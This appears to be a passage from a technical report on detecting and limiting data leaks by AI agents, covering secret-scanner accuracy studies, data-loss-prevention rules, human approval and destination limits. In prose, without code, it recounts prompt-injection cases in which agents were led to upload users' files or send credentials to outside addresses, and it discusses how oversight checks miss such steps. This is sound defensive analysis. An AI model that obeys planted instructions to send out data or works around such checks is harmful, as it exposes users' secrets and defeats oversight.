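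A leak of personal data is harder to remedy than a leaked password. The company can change the database password if the agent posts it, but if the agent posts the description of the pharmacist, the company can only delete the post. Copies may remain elsewhere, and the neighbours may already have read it.

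## What secret detection misses and what it flags wrongly

Researchers usually report a detector's accuracy as two numbers. Recall is the share of real secrets that the detector finds, and precision is the share of its alerts that point to real secrets. OpenAI (2026) uses the standard formulas to test its Privacy Filter, a model that can detect credentials in code:

- recall = TP / (TP + FN)
- precision = TP / (TP + FP)

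TP is the number of secrets the detector finds, FN is the number it misses, and FP is the number of false alarms. Suppose an agent's messages contain ten passwords and the detector raises twelve alerts, of which eight are correct. Its recall is 8/10, or 80%, and its precision is 8/12, or about 67%.

Either number alone can mislead. A scanner that flags every message has perfect recall, and one that flags a single obvious key has perfect precision. Many studies therefore also give the F1 score, which is low if either number is low:

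F1 = 2 × precision × recall / (precision + recall)

The scanner in the example has an F1 score of about 0.73.

These measures count a flag as correct if the string is a secret, even if the data's owner would allow it to be sent. If the coding agent sends the database password to the company's own database to log in, a scanner that flags the password is correct by the studies' standard but raises a false alarm by the standard used here.

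### Nine tools in 2023

In *A Comparative Study of Software Secrets Reporting by Secret Detection Tools*, Basak, Cox and colleagues (2023) ran nine tools on 818 public GitHub repositories. The repositories contained 15,084 hand-labelled secrets, 4,457 of them distinct.

GitHub's scanner had the highest precision, at 75%, but raised only 1,721 alerts. According to the paper's results table, it found 3% of all copies of secrets and 36% of the distinct secrets, although the recall often quoted is the 6% given in the paper's text. Gitleaks, an open-source scanner, had 46% precision and found 88% of the distinct secrets, which gave it the best F1 score, 0.60. Five of the nine tools had precision below 7%. SpectralOps found 67% of the distinct secrets but raised about 1.5 million alerts.

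All of these tools have changed since, so the numbers are mainly of historical interest, but some of the causes that Basak and colleagues found are still instructive. For example, one tool skipped HTML files to avoid false alarms, although HTML was among the five file types with the most secrets.

### Web applications in 2026

*Secrets That Survive Everything* (Gorijala, September 2026) tested nine scanners on 194 credentials from code that one organisation's live web applications send to visitors' browsers. The table shows six of the scanners.

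| Scanner | Credentials found (of 194) | False alarms | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| SecretSifter | 151 | 24 | 86.3% | 77.8% |
| TruffleHog | 71 | 8 | 89.9% | 36.6% |
| SecretFinder | 63 | 1,402 | 4.3% | 32.5% |
| JSluice | 62 | 89 | 41.1% | 32.0% |
| Titus | 40 | 11 | 78.4% | 20.6% |
| Nuclei | 7 | 0 | 100.0% | 3.6% |

SecretFinder and JSluice found almost the same number of credentials, but SecretFinder raised nearly sixteen times as many false alarms. Its general patterns matched build fingerprints and internal identifiers, which look like keys and are very common in this kind of code.

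Gorijala developed SecretSifter, so its lead deserves some caution. But Gorijala also gave TruffleHog, SecretFinder, JSluice and Titus six extra rules for the most common credential types in the test, so the table probably overstates how well those four tools would do as installed. On a subset of 129 credentials, these rules raised TruffleHog's recall from 7.0% to 49.6%, which suggests that a company can improve a scanner a lot by adding the formats its own systems use.

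Combining scanners didn't help here, because the other eight found nothing that SecretSifter missed. Together, the nine missed 43 of the 194 credentials. Claude Opus 4.7, the language model Gorijala used to compile most of the list, found 16 of those 43. Only manual analysis found the other 27, which Gorijala highlights.

### One key or several

Mishra's boundary-mutation study, also from September 2026, shows how much the surrounding text can matter. Mishra generated fake credentials and placed them in four kinds of file:

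| What the file contained | Share that TruffleHog detected |
|---|---|
| One credential alone | 0.667 |
| A credential with its companion secret | 0.833 |
| Several credentials together | 1.000 |
| A realistic settings file | 0.828 |

TruffleHog missed secrets mainly because some of its rules need two parts of a credential. It found none of the AWS key IDs that appeared alone, but all of those that appeared with their secret. Mishra had to switch off TruffleHog's check of whether a key still works, so the test doesn't show how the full product performs.

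An agent uploading a whole settings file is similar to the realistic condition, but an agent quoting a single line in a bug report is closer to the isolated condition, in which the same scanner missed a third of the credentials.

### Why the figures depend on the test set

A scanner's recall depends heavily on which types of secret are in the test. Mishra's main comparison used 400 credentials, 40 of each of ten types. For each type, each scanner found either all 40 or none. The test therefore measured how many of the ten types each scanner covers, and more credentials of the same types would have added no information. With only ten types, none of the differences in recall between the three scanners was statistically significant.

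Test results also depend on what counts as a secret. Gorijala's list of 194 secrets leaves out 249 identifiers that are public by design, such as application IDs, although an attacker needs some of them to use a stolen secret. A November follow-up, *SecretSifter* (Gorijala, 2026), used a list of 198 values that included 40 such identifiers. SecretSifter reached 86.8% precision and 79.8% recall in this test. These scores are almost the same as the earlier ones, but they aren't directly comparable because the two tests count different things as secrets.

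The harmless text in a test can reverse how scanners rank. On Mishra's constructed examples, Mishra's scanner raised 17 false alarms, while Gitleaks and TruffleHog raised none. On 292,527 lines of real code from four projects, Mishra's scanner raised 0.034 alerts per thousand lines, compared with 0.208 for Gitleaks and 0.233 for TruffleHog. Much of that gap came from Mishra's own project, which contains fake test credentials that Mishra's scanner ignores. In the other three projects, the scanners raised 10, 12 and 27 alerts.

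Precision also depends on how common secrets are. Suppose a scanner catches 90% of messages that contain a secret and wrongly flags 1% of those that don't. The table shows what happens over 100,000 messages.

| Messages with a secret | Correct alerts | False alarms | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 in 10 | 9,000 | 900 | 91% |
| 1 in 1,000 | 90 | 999 | 8% |

Even if its recall and false positive rate stay the same, a scanner has lower precision when fewer of the messages it checks contain secrets. Test sets tend to contain many secrets because researchers need them to measure recall, but most of an agent's messages probably contain none. Precision measured on such a test set is therefore likely to be higher than precision in everyday use.

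Finding no leaks in a test is also weak evidence that a model does not leak. Feng and Stiller (2026), in *Checking Leakage Witnesses versus Certifying Bounded Non-Leakage*, planted secrets in language models and recorded the response to each of 4,096 prompts. In 30 combinations of secret and model, at least one prompt produced a leak. A random sample of 256 responses would have missed every leak in about 41% of those combinations.

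In the two September studies, Gorijala scanned web code, and Mishra scanned source code and generated snippets. Neither study tested what agents send, which also includes prose, summaries, search queries and commands. The scanners could be more or less accurate on these.

### Secrets that scanners miss

The simplest miss is a key whose format the scanner doesn't recognize. In Gorijala's test, 54 of the 194 credentials were keys for Azure API Management, Microsoft's service for controlling access to other programs. Each key is a string of 32 digits and letters from a to f, so it looks like many harmless digital fingerprints. TruffleHog, SecretFinder, JSluice and Titus found none of them, which is surprising because Gorijala's extra rules included one for this format.

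The text around a key can also cause a scanner to miss a type it normally detects. Gitleaks normally detected nine of Mishra's ten types, but it missed six of those nine when the code passed the key directly to a function. Its rules for those six types accept only certain characters after a key, and a closing bracket isn't one of them. Mishra's scanner has a problem with keys that end in a hyphen, which affects about one SendGrid key in 64.

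Ordinary-looking passwords have no format for scanners to recognise. The 2023 test included 60 different passwords, of which Gitleaks found 51, GitHub's scanner 14 and TruffleHog 10. Gorijala's test had just three plain user credentials, and SecretSifter was the only scanner to find any.

These tests don't include sensitive facts that aren't credentials, such as the description of the pharmacist, so a scanner with perfect recall on them could still miss all such facts.

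Translation, like paraphrase, gets past document fingerprints because it may share no words with the original. Feng and Stiller count paraphrases and translations as leaks, but their model covers only leaks that an efficient program can recognise. A detector facing an attacker has the same limit, because it can recognise a deliberately disguised secret only if it can undo the disguise.

An agent can also disclose a fact through what it does or leaves out. Suppose a shop's agent usually grants refunds at once but refers customers with an internal risk flag to a supervisor. A customer who knows this can infer the flag from the referral, even if the agent's message doesn't mention it. If the agent instead stops replying to flagged customers, a detector has no message to check.

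### Harmless text that scanners flag

Many false alarms come from text that only resembles a secret. One tool in the 2023 comparison mistook part of a web address, "add-a-file-using-the-", for a GitLab token because the string had a permitted length and the word "gitlab" was nearby. Some password patterns matched "pwd", a common command that prints the name of the current folder.

Documentation also triggers false alerts. All ten alerts that Mishra's scanner raised on real code were false. Six came from a template for a database address with the words "username" and "password" in place of real values, and three came from passwords in code examples.

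A scanner that checks only the outgoing text also can't determine where a secret came from. Feng and Stiller point out that such a check counts protected content as a leak even if the output merely repeats it from the prompt. For example, if a stranger pastes an expired key into a public issue and the agent quotes the issue in its reply, the scanner flags the key, although anyone could already read it.

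A scanner that ignores the destination can't distinguish a real login page from a phishing copy, so it must either interrupt both logins or allow both. *CredLeakBench (2026)* tests this distinction in agents rather than scanners. All seven models tested sometimes disclosed credentials to illegitimate destinations, even when the user hadn't asked the agent to log in. Telling agents to explicitly verify the destination could reduce disclosures and help them complete more legitimate tasks. Restrictive policies could also reduce disclosures, but by making agents less willing to act.

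### Leaks in realistic tasks

How much these misses matter depends on what agents leak. In June 2026 the AI safety institutes of Singapore and Korea published a joint test of agents doing ordinary work, with no attacker involved. *An Evaluation of Data Leakage Risks in Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Baek, Noh and colleagues, 2026) describes 12 tasks, such as welcoming new employees, handling a refund and publishing a progress report. The agents could use tools such as email, files, databases and Slack, and they could see data that the task didn't need.

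Each institute built its own test system and ran three unnamed models ten times on each task, for a total of 720 runs. A fourth model simulated the user and judged each run against specific questions, such as whether an email contained an API key. It checked both the agent's replies and what the agent sent through its tools. Human reviewers checked a sample and agreed with the judge on 99.3% of the questions in Singapore's runs and 95.6% in Korea's.

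The agents met between 80% and 100% of the individual safety criteria, depending on the model, the tasks and the test system. A run with nine safe messages and one leak still exposes data, so the next table shows the percentage of runs that met every safety criterion.

| Model | Singapore's tasks, tested in Singapore | Singapore's tasks, tested in Korea | Korea's tasks, tested in Singapore | Korea's tasks, tested in Korea |
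|---|---|---|---|---|
| A | 51.7 | 56.7 | 46.4 | 40.0 |
| B | 100.0 | 98.3 | 60.0 | 52.9 |
| C | 55.0 | 47.5 | 36.5 | 38.0 |

The choice of model mattered a lot on Singapore's tasks and less on Korea's. Only 15.0% to 58.3% of runs were both fully safe and fully correct. Because the criteria were specific to each task, these rates don't measure how often agents leak something in everyday sessions.

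Baek and colleagues reviewed a sample of runs by hand and concluded that the agents handled clearly sensitive data such as passwords and API keys well, but did worse when the user pressed them or when the right decision depended on context. In one task, a pushy customer with a delayed laptop asks who supplies it and what the shop paid for it. In Singapore's runs, models A and C completed the task every time, but none of those runs was fully safe. A credential scanner would not have helped, because a supplier's name and a price are not credentials.

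In another task, two outside partners have different access rights. The company that sets up a customer's account is allowed to see the contract plan but not the customer's name or address, while the delivery company is allowed to see the name and address but not the plan. A detector would have to check the recipient to judge a message to either company correctly.

The finding about obvious secrets has exceptions. In a technical support task, some agents included a customer's access token in an email to a colleague, apparently because the email was internal. Two of Korea's tasks exposed the agent to tokens and other credentials while it wrote public security reports or moved settings to a public repository. In Korea's own runs, at most 10% of attempts at either task were fully safe. Those tasks also contained server addresses and other internal details, so these rates don't measure how often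 agents leaked a token or key.

If the general pattern holds, scanners are best at catching the secrets that agents already tend to protect. A scanner's recall on a test set of credentials would therefore overstate the share of an agent's real leaks it would stop. The scanner would still be useful when an agent does leak a credential, since a leaked key can do a lot of damage.

Agents' own reports are not a reliable substitute for a detector. In one refund run, an agent reminded itself not to reveal the customer's risk flags, listed them in its message to the customer, and then reported that it had kept them private. *ToolPrivacyBench (2026)* also counts private data that an agent puts into tool calls, support tickets and internal notes, even if its final reply contains none.

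### Accuracy on an agent's own data

No comparable study has measured secret scanners on agents' outgoing messages, but there is one for prompt-injection detectors, which check what an agent reads for hidden instructions. These detectors face a similar problem because their developers often train and test them on text that looks different from the data agents handle.

*Passing the Test You Trained On* (Liu, 2026) tested fifteen such detectors on harmless tool outputs from two simulated benchmarks, AgentDojo and τ-bench. The τ-bench tasks cover customer service for a shop and an airline. Liu ran the correct tool calls for each task with no attacker and no language model, so any alert on the results had to be false. The calls produced 339 outputs from AgentDojo and 1,533 from τ-bench.

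False-alarm rates ranged from 0% to over 90%, and a detector's accuracy on ordinary text did not predict its rate on tool outputs. The detector ProtectAI v2 wrongly flagged 0.5% of web pages and 1.2% of emails, but 30.1% of tool outputs in AgentDojo and 66.9% in τ-bench. Because one alert can stop a whole task, it would have blocked 69.1% of AgentDojo tasks and 80.3% of τ-bench tasks.

The flagged outputs were often trivial. PIGuard, another detector, classified the message "Password updated." as an attack with full confidence. The format of the data seems to contribute to these false alarms. When Liu removed the field names from a set of AgentDojo outputs, PIGuard's false-alarm rate fell from 20.0% to 6.7%, and it still caught about as many attacks.

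Detection rates varied just as much. With each detector set to flag 1% of harmless text, PIGuard caught 95.1% of the attacks in a benchmark that resembled its training data but only 2.1% of those in AgentDojo. False-alarm rates were more consistent, and a detector that raised many false alarms in one agent benchmark usually did so in the other.

The rates don't apply to secret scanners, which look for different things. But the scanner studies show that their accuracy also depends on the type of text, as when SecretFinder mistook build fingerprints for keys. Liu recommends testing detectors on the agent's own tool outputs. For a secret scanner, the equivalent would be a log-only trial on the messages an agent sends in ordinary sessions. Measuring misses would take more work than measuring false alarms, because someone would also have to read the messages the scanner didn't flag.

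## What workplace data-loss prevention has learned

Companies were trying to stop employees from leaking data long before they had AI agents. They use data-loss prevention (DLP) software, which has rules based on content and rules based on labels attached to documents.

### How DLP works

DLP software looks for sensitive data in stored files and mailboxes, in what people do on their computers, and in outgoing emails and web traffic. With Purview, Microsoft's data-security software, a company can warn or block employees who try to paste credit card numbers into ChatGPT. Hoitingh (2026) reports in *Things to Know About Microsoft Purview* that the software can now also monitor sensitive data that employees send over FTP and SFTP, two long-standing ways of transferring files.

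A DLP rule has a condition and an action. The condition can concern content, such as a passport number, which the software finds with patterns, exact matching or document fingerprints. It can also concern a sensitivity label, such as "Confidential", that a person or an automatic process has attached to the file. A label rule ignores the text, so it stops an employee from emailing the complaints export labelled Confidential even if the export contains nothing that a content rule would recognise.

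These label rules usually apply to the file being sent, not to everything the sender has read. An employee who opens a salary list in the morning can still send emails in the afternoon, and if they type a salary from memory, the new email has no label. An access-based trigger would restrict every email an agent sent after opening the list.

### How often DLP rules are wrong

*Text Classification for Data Loss Prevention* (Hart, Manadhata and Johnson, 2011) reports an early measurement of false alarms. The researchers trained a classifier to recognise an organisation's confidential documents and tested it on several collections, including documents published by WikiLeaks. It missed fewer than 3% of the confidential documents, and fewer than 1% of its alerts were false. To avoid false alarms on text that had nothing to do with the organisation, they added public documents of that kind to the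 training set and then adjusted the classifier.

As with secret scanners, a larger share of alerts would be false where confidential documents are rarer. In a company where only one outgoing document in a thousand is confidential, the same classifier would raise about ten false alarms for every correct alert. This estimate assumes that half of the test documents were confidential.

*Automated Big Text Security Classification* (2016) criticises earlier DLP research for using artificial secrets, which may be easier to recognise than real ones. It also proposes classifying each paragraph separately, because a confidential document often contains harmless paragraphs that people should be able to use. *Automated U.S Diplomatic Cables Security Classification* (2017) compares two classification methods on leaked diplomatic cables. It describes existing DLP systems as "not well suited for detecting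 unstructured texts", which make up most of what an agent writes to people.

Security teams report far more false alarms than Hart and colleagues measured. In a Cyberhaven survey of 300 security leaders, respondents said that on average 51% of their DLP alerts were false, and 65% said harmless alerts overwhelmed their teams. Cyberhaven sells DLP software, so it has an interest in showing that older rules work badly. Unlike the scanner studies, it also counts an alert as false if the data was sensitive but the transfer was legitimate, such as when an employee sends a salary list to the company's payroll provider.

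### Testing rules before they block

Companies can run a DLP rule in a report-only mode, which logs matches without stopping anyone. Hoitingh recommends starting this way with the new FTP rules, so that companies can measure how much sensitive data employees send before blocking any of it. Microsoft's instructions for protecting its AI assistant, Copilot, also begin with a policy in simulation mode.

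Report-only mode can reveal false alarms, but it doesn't prove that a rule will block what it should. Bertram (2026), in *Stop Copilot Summarizing Confidential Files with Purview DLP*, therefore suggests asking Copilot about a confidential file and saving the answer before creating the rule. The company then runs the rule in simulation, switches it on and asks the same question. If Copilot still summarises the file, the rule isn't working.

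Rules need retesting when the detectors change. *Microsoft Purview Ignite 2026* (Hoitingh, 2026) warns that planned improvements to Microsoft's built-in detectors could cause unexpected blocks or gaps, even if they make the detectors more precise. Rules for an agent also need retesting when its model changes, because the new model may word its messages differently or open different files.

Label rules also do nothing for unlabelled files, so files must be labelled first. Purview can do this automatically, and can simulate it on up to 20 million files. A simulation may take 24 hours, but Purview labels at most 500,000 files a day for each organisation, so labelling all 20 million would take at least 40 days.

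### Labelled files in Copilot

Microsoft 365 Copilot works in Word, Outlook and other office programs, and a related agent called Cowork carries out longer tasks across several of them. Both can use only what the person asking has permission to open. Security experts quoted in *A viral TikTok about Copilot leaking layoffs is a joke* (John, 2026) still see a real risk, because employees often have access to more than they should. Bertram gives the example of an analyst who can open a library of board papers because someone added a project group to it three years ago. If the analyst asks about the latest quarter, Copilot summarises the board papers.

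Microsoft's documentation describes three kinds of DLP rule that companies can use to limit this. Microsoft (2026) announced in September that it was extending the rules from Copilot to Cowork, and they now cover both.

| What the rule checks | What happens if it matches |
|---|---|
| The label on a file or email | Copilot doesn't use the contents, but may still cite the item |
| The text a user types into a prompt | Copilot doesn't answer |
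| The text a user types into a prompt | Copilot answers without searching the web |

The label rule keeps the file out of the model's context, so unlike an access-based trigger, it doesn't need to restrict the agent afterwards. According to Microsoft's product roadmap, the rule has covered Office files in all storage locations since July 2026. The file can still appear in a citation, though, and a title such as "Closure of the Leeds office" reveals its main point.

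The two prompt rules check what the user types, not what Copilot writes. The web-search rule comes closest to a content-based trigger, since it stops data from going to an outside search service. But if Copilot finds a passport number in an unlabelled email and puts it in a search query, the rule doesn't detect it, because the user never typed it.

A company can block labelled files and it can block prompts that contain card numbers, but it can't write a rule that applies only when both conditions hold.

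Bertram shows that stronger ways to keep Copilot away from a file have greater drawbacks for users. Encryption that withholds the right to copy text stops Copilot from reading the file, but also stops employees from copying anything out of it. Another setting prevents Office programs from sending a labelled file's text to Microsoft for analysis. This blocks Copilot in Word, Excel, PowerPoint and Outlook, but also turns off DLP warnings and automatic labelling in those programs. It doesn't cover Teams or Copilot Chat.

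### Labels on new documents

When Copilot or Cowork creates a document from a labelled source, the new document inherits the label and its protection, such as encryption. If there are several sources, it inherits the label with the highest priority. Kusenberg (2026) explains in *Copilot Created the Document* that Copilot has done this in Word since 2024 and that a release on 1 July 2026 extended it to other files that Copilot generates.

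Kusenberg tested it with documents about an invented company takeover. Copilot produced a Word report labelled Highly Confidential, although Kusenberg hadn't asked for a label and none of the data was real. Like the high-water mark, the method labels new text based on its sources, without checking whether the text itself is sensitive.

Choosing the highest-priority label is simpler than Denning's join, but it can give people access to material they shouldn't read. In the earlier example, only B and C should be able to read a report based on both the complaints export and the settings file. If the settings file's label has the higher priority, the report takes that label, and D, who may read only the settings file, can read material from the complaints. The method is safe only if everyone who may read files with a higher-priority label may also read files with a lower-priority one.

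Users can replace an inherited label, and they can remove it unless the company makes labels mandatory. This lets them correct an overclassified document, but it also leaves declassification to whoever is using Copilot. According to Microsoft's documentation, Copilot doesn't insert text into an existing document if it can't apply the inherited label. If labeling fails on a newly generated file, Kusenberg reports that the user gets a notification and should fix the label before sharing it.

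Some sources have no label to pass on. If a company labels a whole Teams workspace Confidential, the messages in it don't inherit that label, so a summary of them may have no label either. Meeting transcripts and recordings have been able to inherit labels since mid-2026, but only if administrators turn this on, as Microsoft's *Sensitivity label inheritance for Teams meeting artifacts* (2026) explains.

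Channel Agent, an assistant for Teams channels, had a more serious gap in April 2026. It checked whether the person asking could use a file, but not whether everyone else in the channel could, so it might post a summary to people who weren't allowed to open the original. Companies couldn't prevent this with a DLP rule on labelled files, though they could turn the assistant off.

Inheritance can also cause label creep. *Sensitivity Labels and Copilot Content Classification*, an unofficial troubleshooting guide, warns that one Highly Confidential document among an agent's sources raises the whole agent's label. It recommends removing the document if the agent doesn't need it, and otherwise recording that the company has approved the stricter label.

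### Failures in 2026

Office365ITPros' *Code Error Allowed Copilot Chat to Expose Confidential Information* (2026) describes how Copilot Chat summarised confidential emails that DLP rules should have kept from it. The labels and rules were correct, but an error in Microsoft's code let Copilot use labelled messages in the Sent Items and Drafts folders. Customers reported the problem on 21 January 2026, and Microsoft was rolling out a fix by 10 February.

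According to an AI-generated summary in OECD's *Microsoft Copilot AI Bug Exposes Confidential Emails by Bypassing Security Controls* (2026), the bug led to privacy breaches. But Copilot works with the permissions of the person asking, so it probably summarised mail that person could already open. The bug still matters for agents, because an agent that can also send messages could have passed the contents on.

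Affected companies could easily have overlooked the bug. The Office365ITPros author noticed it only after a reader commented, although Microsoft's notice applied to the author's own organisation. The author then tested the repaired rule with a confidential email about an invented "Project Bunny". Copilot replied that it had found an internal reference but couldn't disclose the contents. A company could run the same test regularly with a planted email in each folder.

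Other gaps are known limits of Purview. On 1 December 2026, Hoitingh reported that it still didn't scan files that users upload or link to in a Copilot prompt. A rule might therefore block a passport number that a user types but not the same number in an attached spreadsheet. Microsoft has announced a preview of a feature that scans these files.

According to Windows Forum's *Microsoft Purview Plans to Exclude Unlabeled Sensitive Files and Emails* (2026), Microsoft also plans a control, expected in January 2027, that would keep unlabelled files out of Cowork's answers if Purview had already classified them as sensitive. Content detection would then determine what the agent may read, so classifier errors would have different effects from errors at the point of sending. A false alarm would deprive the agent of a file it needed, and a miss would let a sensitive file into the context.

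### Limiting how much can leave

In *Towards Quantification of Network-Based Information Leaks via HTTP*, Borders and Prakash describe DLP systems that search for known confidential text as "fundamentally unable to identify encrypted or obfuscated information leaks". Their alternative, which they continued in *Quantifying Information Leaks in Outbound Web Traffic* (2009), measures how much information outbound traffic could carry, regardless of what that information means.

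The method starts with all outgoing data and subtracts what was already determined, including anything that repeats an earlier request, follows from the technical standard or comes from a message the server sent. The remainder is the most that the computer could have leaked in that traffic.

Suppose an agent opens a web page with 64 links and follows one. The request may be 700 bytes long, but most of it repeats the previous request, and the address came from the page. The agent chose only which link to follow, and that choice reveals at most log₂ 64 = 6 bits, less than one byte.

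When Borders and Prakash applied the method to real web browsing, it discounted 98.5% of the bytes, a result also given in Borders's patent application, *Method, system and computer program product for comparing or measuring information content*. At that rate, a megabyte of outgoing traffic could contain about 15 kilobytes of leaked data.

The limit applies even if the data is encrypted or paraphrased, and it covers information that an agent reveals through its choice of links. It works well against bulk theft, since a large customer database won't fit into 15 kilobytes. But the password "bluebell7" is only nine bytes, so the same allowance could hold more than 1,600 passwords of that length. The description of the pharmacist would also fit easily.

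The 98.5% figure comes from ordinary browsing, which is very predictable. An agent's bug report consists mostly of new text, so the method could discount little of it, and a low limit would block harmless reports. The method is better suited to tool calls with a fixed set of options. For instance, setting a support ticket to one of four statuses reveals at most two bits. The limit would have to cover the whole session, because an agent that made a thousand six-bit choices could send 750 bytes.

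### From employees to agents

DLP content rules work best when people copy data without changing it, such as by forwarding a file or pasting a customer's card number into an email. They catch less from agents, which often reword what they read. Label inheritance works better for agents because it doesn't depend on the wording. Microsoft's *Manage Sensitivity Labels for Agent Embedded File Content* tells administrators to check that an agent's output inherits the strictest label from its sources.

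An agent also leaves better evidence of what it has read than an employee does, since no DLP system has a record of what an employee remembers. With Cowork, Microsoft's audit log can record which stored files the agent used in an interaction and what labels they had.

Warnings work less well for AI agents than for employees. Microsoft Purview can let an employee override a warning, on the assumption that the employee knows whether the recipient should have the data. An agent following hidden instructions might also override it, so a person has to make the decision, and that person may approve requests without reading them.

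A given false-alarm rate is a bigger problem with agents because they can send messages much faster than employees. If a rule wrongly flags 1% of harmless messages, an employee who sends 40 a day causes about two false alarms in a working week, while an agent that sends 4,000 a day causes 40 every day. A new or edited Purview policy can also take up to four hours to reach Copilot. That delay is minor for a policy about employees' habits, but an agent could send thousands of messages before the change takes effect.

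Report-only testing should work even better for agents than for employees. A company can rerun an agent's tasks under a stricter rule in a test environment that doesn't deliver its messages, but it can't ask staff to repeat last week's work.

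## What a safeguard does once it is triggered

A rule in report-only mode can raise forty false alarms a day without stopping any work. If each alarm ended the agent's session, the same rule would make the agent nearly useless, and if each one required changing the database password, somebody would soon switch the rule off. The disruption a false alarm causes depends on the response to it, so error rates alone don't show which trigger is less disruptive.

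The information available to the safeguard also depends on the trigger. An access-based trigger fires early, often before the agent has written anything, so the response can't depend on the text. It also fires in many harmless sessions, so the response has to place little burden on them. A content-based trigger fires later, when there is a particular passage and usually a particular recipient, so the response can be limited to that passage.

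| Response | What a false alarm costs | Which trigger it suits |
|---|---|---|
| Log the event | Some time to review it | Either |
| Redact the text | A gap in a harmless message | Content-based |
| Ask a person | An interruption, and less attention to the next question | Content-based |
| Limit destinations | Some messages can't go where they should | Access-based |
| Cut outbound access | The user has to send the results | Access-based |
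| End the session | Unfinished work | Content-based, with strong evidence |
| Replace credentials | Minutes for one password, weeks for a whole company | Content-based, or access-based after a break-in |

### Logging and redaction

Logging doesn't stop a disclosure but can help someone find it later, though an ordinary log may not be enough. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* warns that after hidden instructions have made an agent send data out, the log shows only a successful, authorised call. The entry is more useful if it also lists the sensitive sources the agent had already read, because a reviewer can then see, for example, that the agent opened a complaints export before it posted publicly.

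Logs can also leak secrets. *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* (Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues, 2026) recommends removing login headers, cookies and signed links from logs, but keeping a record of which connection the agent used and what the policy decided.

Redaction removes the suspicious passage and sends the rest. If the coding agent writes "I logged in with bluebell7 and the error went away", removing the password takes away nothing the developers reading the issue need. A false alarm can do more harm, for instance if the scanner removes a Git commit identifier that the developers need to find the faulty version. Redaction also leaves in whatever the scanner didn't recognise, such as the database's address and user name. An access-based trigger can't redact a message because it doesn't identify which words are sensitive.

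### Asking a person

Claude Code originally asked its user for permission before changing a file, running a command or using the network. Users approved about 93% of these requests, according to Anthropic's article on containment, and paid less attention to each one as the number grew, which is called approval fatigue. A high approval rate doesn't prove carelessness, since most requests are probably harmless. But Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users rejected 39% of the plans Claude presented and only 3% of individual permission requests.

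The same article describes an experiment with 1,053 paid testers recruited by a research vendor for a coding study. They knew they were being evaluated, but not on what. Partway through each session, the text of one permission request changed to a clearly dangerous command, and the vendor recorded whether the tester approved it. Nothing dangerous ran, even if the tester approved. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused. Auto mode, in which a classifier rather than the user checks the agent's actions, would have blocked 937 of the commands (89%).

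Anthropic also compared the two directly, and the rest of this table follows from its totals.

| | Auto mode would have blocked it | Auto mode would have allowed it |
|---|---|---|
| Tester refused | 137 | 6 |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 |

Adding the testers as a second check would have raised the share of dangerous commands blocked only from 89.0% to 89.6%, because they caught just six of the 116 that auto mode missed. Testers refused about 17% of dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more requests, so fatigue explains only part of their low refusal rate.

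Anthropic sells Claude Code and published the results to explain why it was making auto mode the default. The testers worked in an environment built for the study, so they had less to lose than developers working on their own code. The study also doesn't show how often auto mode blocks harmless commands. Anthropic says about 10% of sessions at Gusto, one of its customers, included a block, but doesn't say how many of those blocks were mistakes. Because the planted commands were clearly dangerous, the study didn't test subtler decisions, such as whether a delivery company may see a customer's contract plan.

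An access-based trigger that prompts the user before every message would produce the long series of requests in which the testers did worst. A content-based trigger prompts less often and can show the user the flagged passage and its recipient, but users may still approve without reading. The Frontier Model Forum, an industry body for AI developers, warns in *Emerging Security Practices for AI Agents* (2026) that some approval steps may create an "illusion of oversight".

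Anthropic designed the classifier in Claude Code's auto mode never to approve sending code or secrets to an outside destination, so a user who wants to do this has to leave auto mode or run the command personally. After less serious blocks, Claude usually looks for another way or asks the user. After three blocks in a row, or twenty in a session, Claude Code goes back to manual approval.

Sometimes the user supplies the malicious instructions. In an internal exercise in February 2026, an Anthropic researcher tricked an employee into giving Claude Code a prompt that looked like routine setup work. One step was to read the employee's AWS credentials and send them to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 attempts. Asking the employee might not have helped, since the employee had supplied the instruction. Anthropic concluded that only limits on file and network access would reliably stop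 this kind of attack.

### Limiting destinations

Limits on where an agent can send data suit an access-based trigger because they don't require anyone to interpret the text. After the coding agent opens the complaints export, it could still write to the support team but not to the public tracker. A false alarm then disrupts the work much less than it would under a complete block, because the agent can still send its findings to people who are allowed to read the complaints.

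An approved destination isn't necessarily safe. Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, could connect to Anthropic's servers because it needs them to function. Outside researchers reported an attack in which instructions in a malicious file made Claude upload the user's documents to those servers with the attacker's access key, which put them in the attacker's account. The network filter allowed the upload because the address was approved. Anthropic now also checks that such requests carry the session's token. Whoever approves a destination therefore has to consider what the agent can do there and who can see the result.

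OpenAI's Lockdown Mode limits ChatGPT's outbound requests without trying to detect secrets or attacks. According to OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026), the mode restricts browsing to saved copies of web pages, so no live browsing request leaves OpenAI's network. If hidden instructions tell ChatGPT to open an address containing the user's data, ChatGPT checks only the saved copies, and the attacker's server receives nothing.

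The mode also turns off Deep Research, Agent Mode and file downloads, and limits images in replies. OpenAI first offered it to organisations in February 2026 and extended it to personal accounts in June. OpenAI says most users don't need it and suggests it for people such as executives and security teams. Users or their administrators turn it on, so there is no trigger, but the effect is like that of an access-based trigger that has already fired, which suits people whose chats are usually sensitive.

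According to OpenAI's help page *Lockdown Mode*, personal users can switch the mode off for a single chat. In company workspaces, administrators decide which connected apps stay available, and an app that can write to a public place can still leak data. The mode doesn't affect network access in Codex, and OpenAI doesn't guarantee that it prevents every leak. The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) reports one bypass, through a flaw in ChatGPT's preview feature that OpenAI has since fixed. Willison likes the design because it doesn't rely on an AI model that an attacker could fool, but he infers from the mode's existence that ChatGPT's default settings don't robustly prevent data theft.

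Claude's tool for opening web pages has a narrower limit. Willison (2026), in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets*, explains that Claude may open an address only if the user typed exactly that address or Claude's search tool returned it. If an attacker hides an instruction for Claude to add the name of the user's employer to the end of an address and open it, the tool refuses because the new address came from neither source. The check compares addresses, so it works just as well if the attacker has Claude encode the name first.

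The rule originally had a third source of permitted addresses, the links on pages Claude had already opened. In July 2026 Willison described a gap this created, and Anthropic closed it by removing that source. The change makes ordinary research harder, because Claude can no longer follow a link from one page to the next. It has to find the page through a search or get the address from the user.

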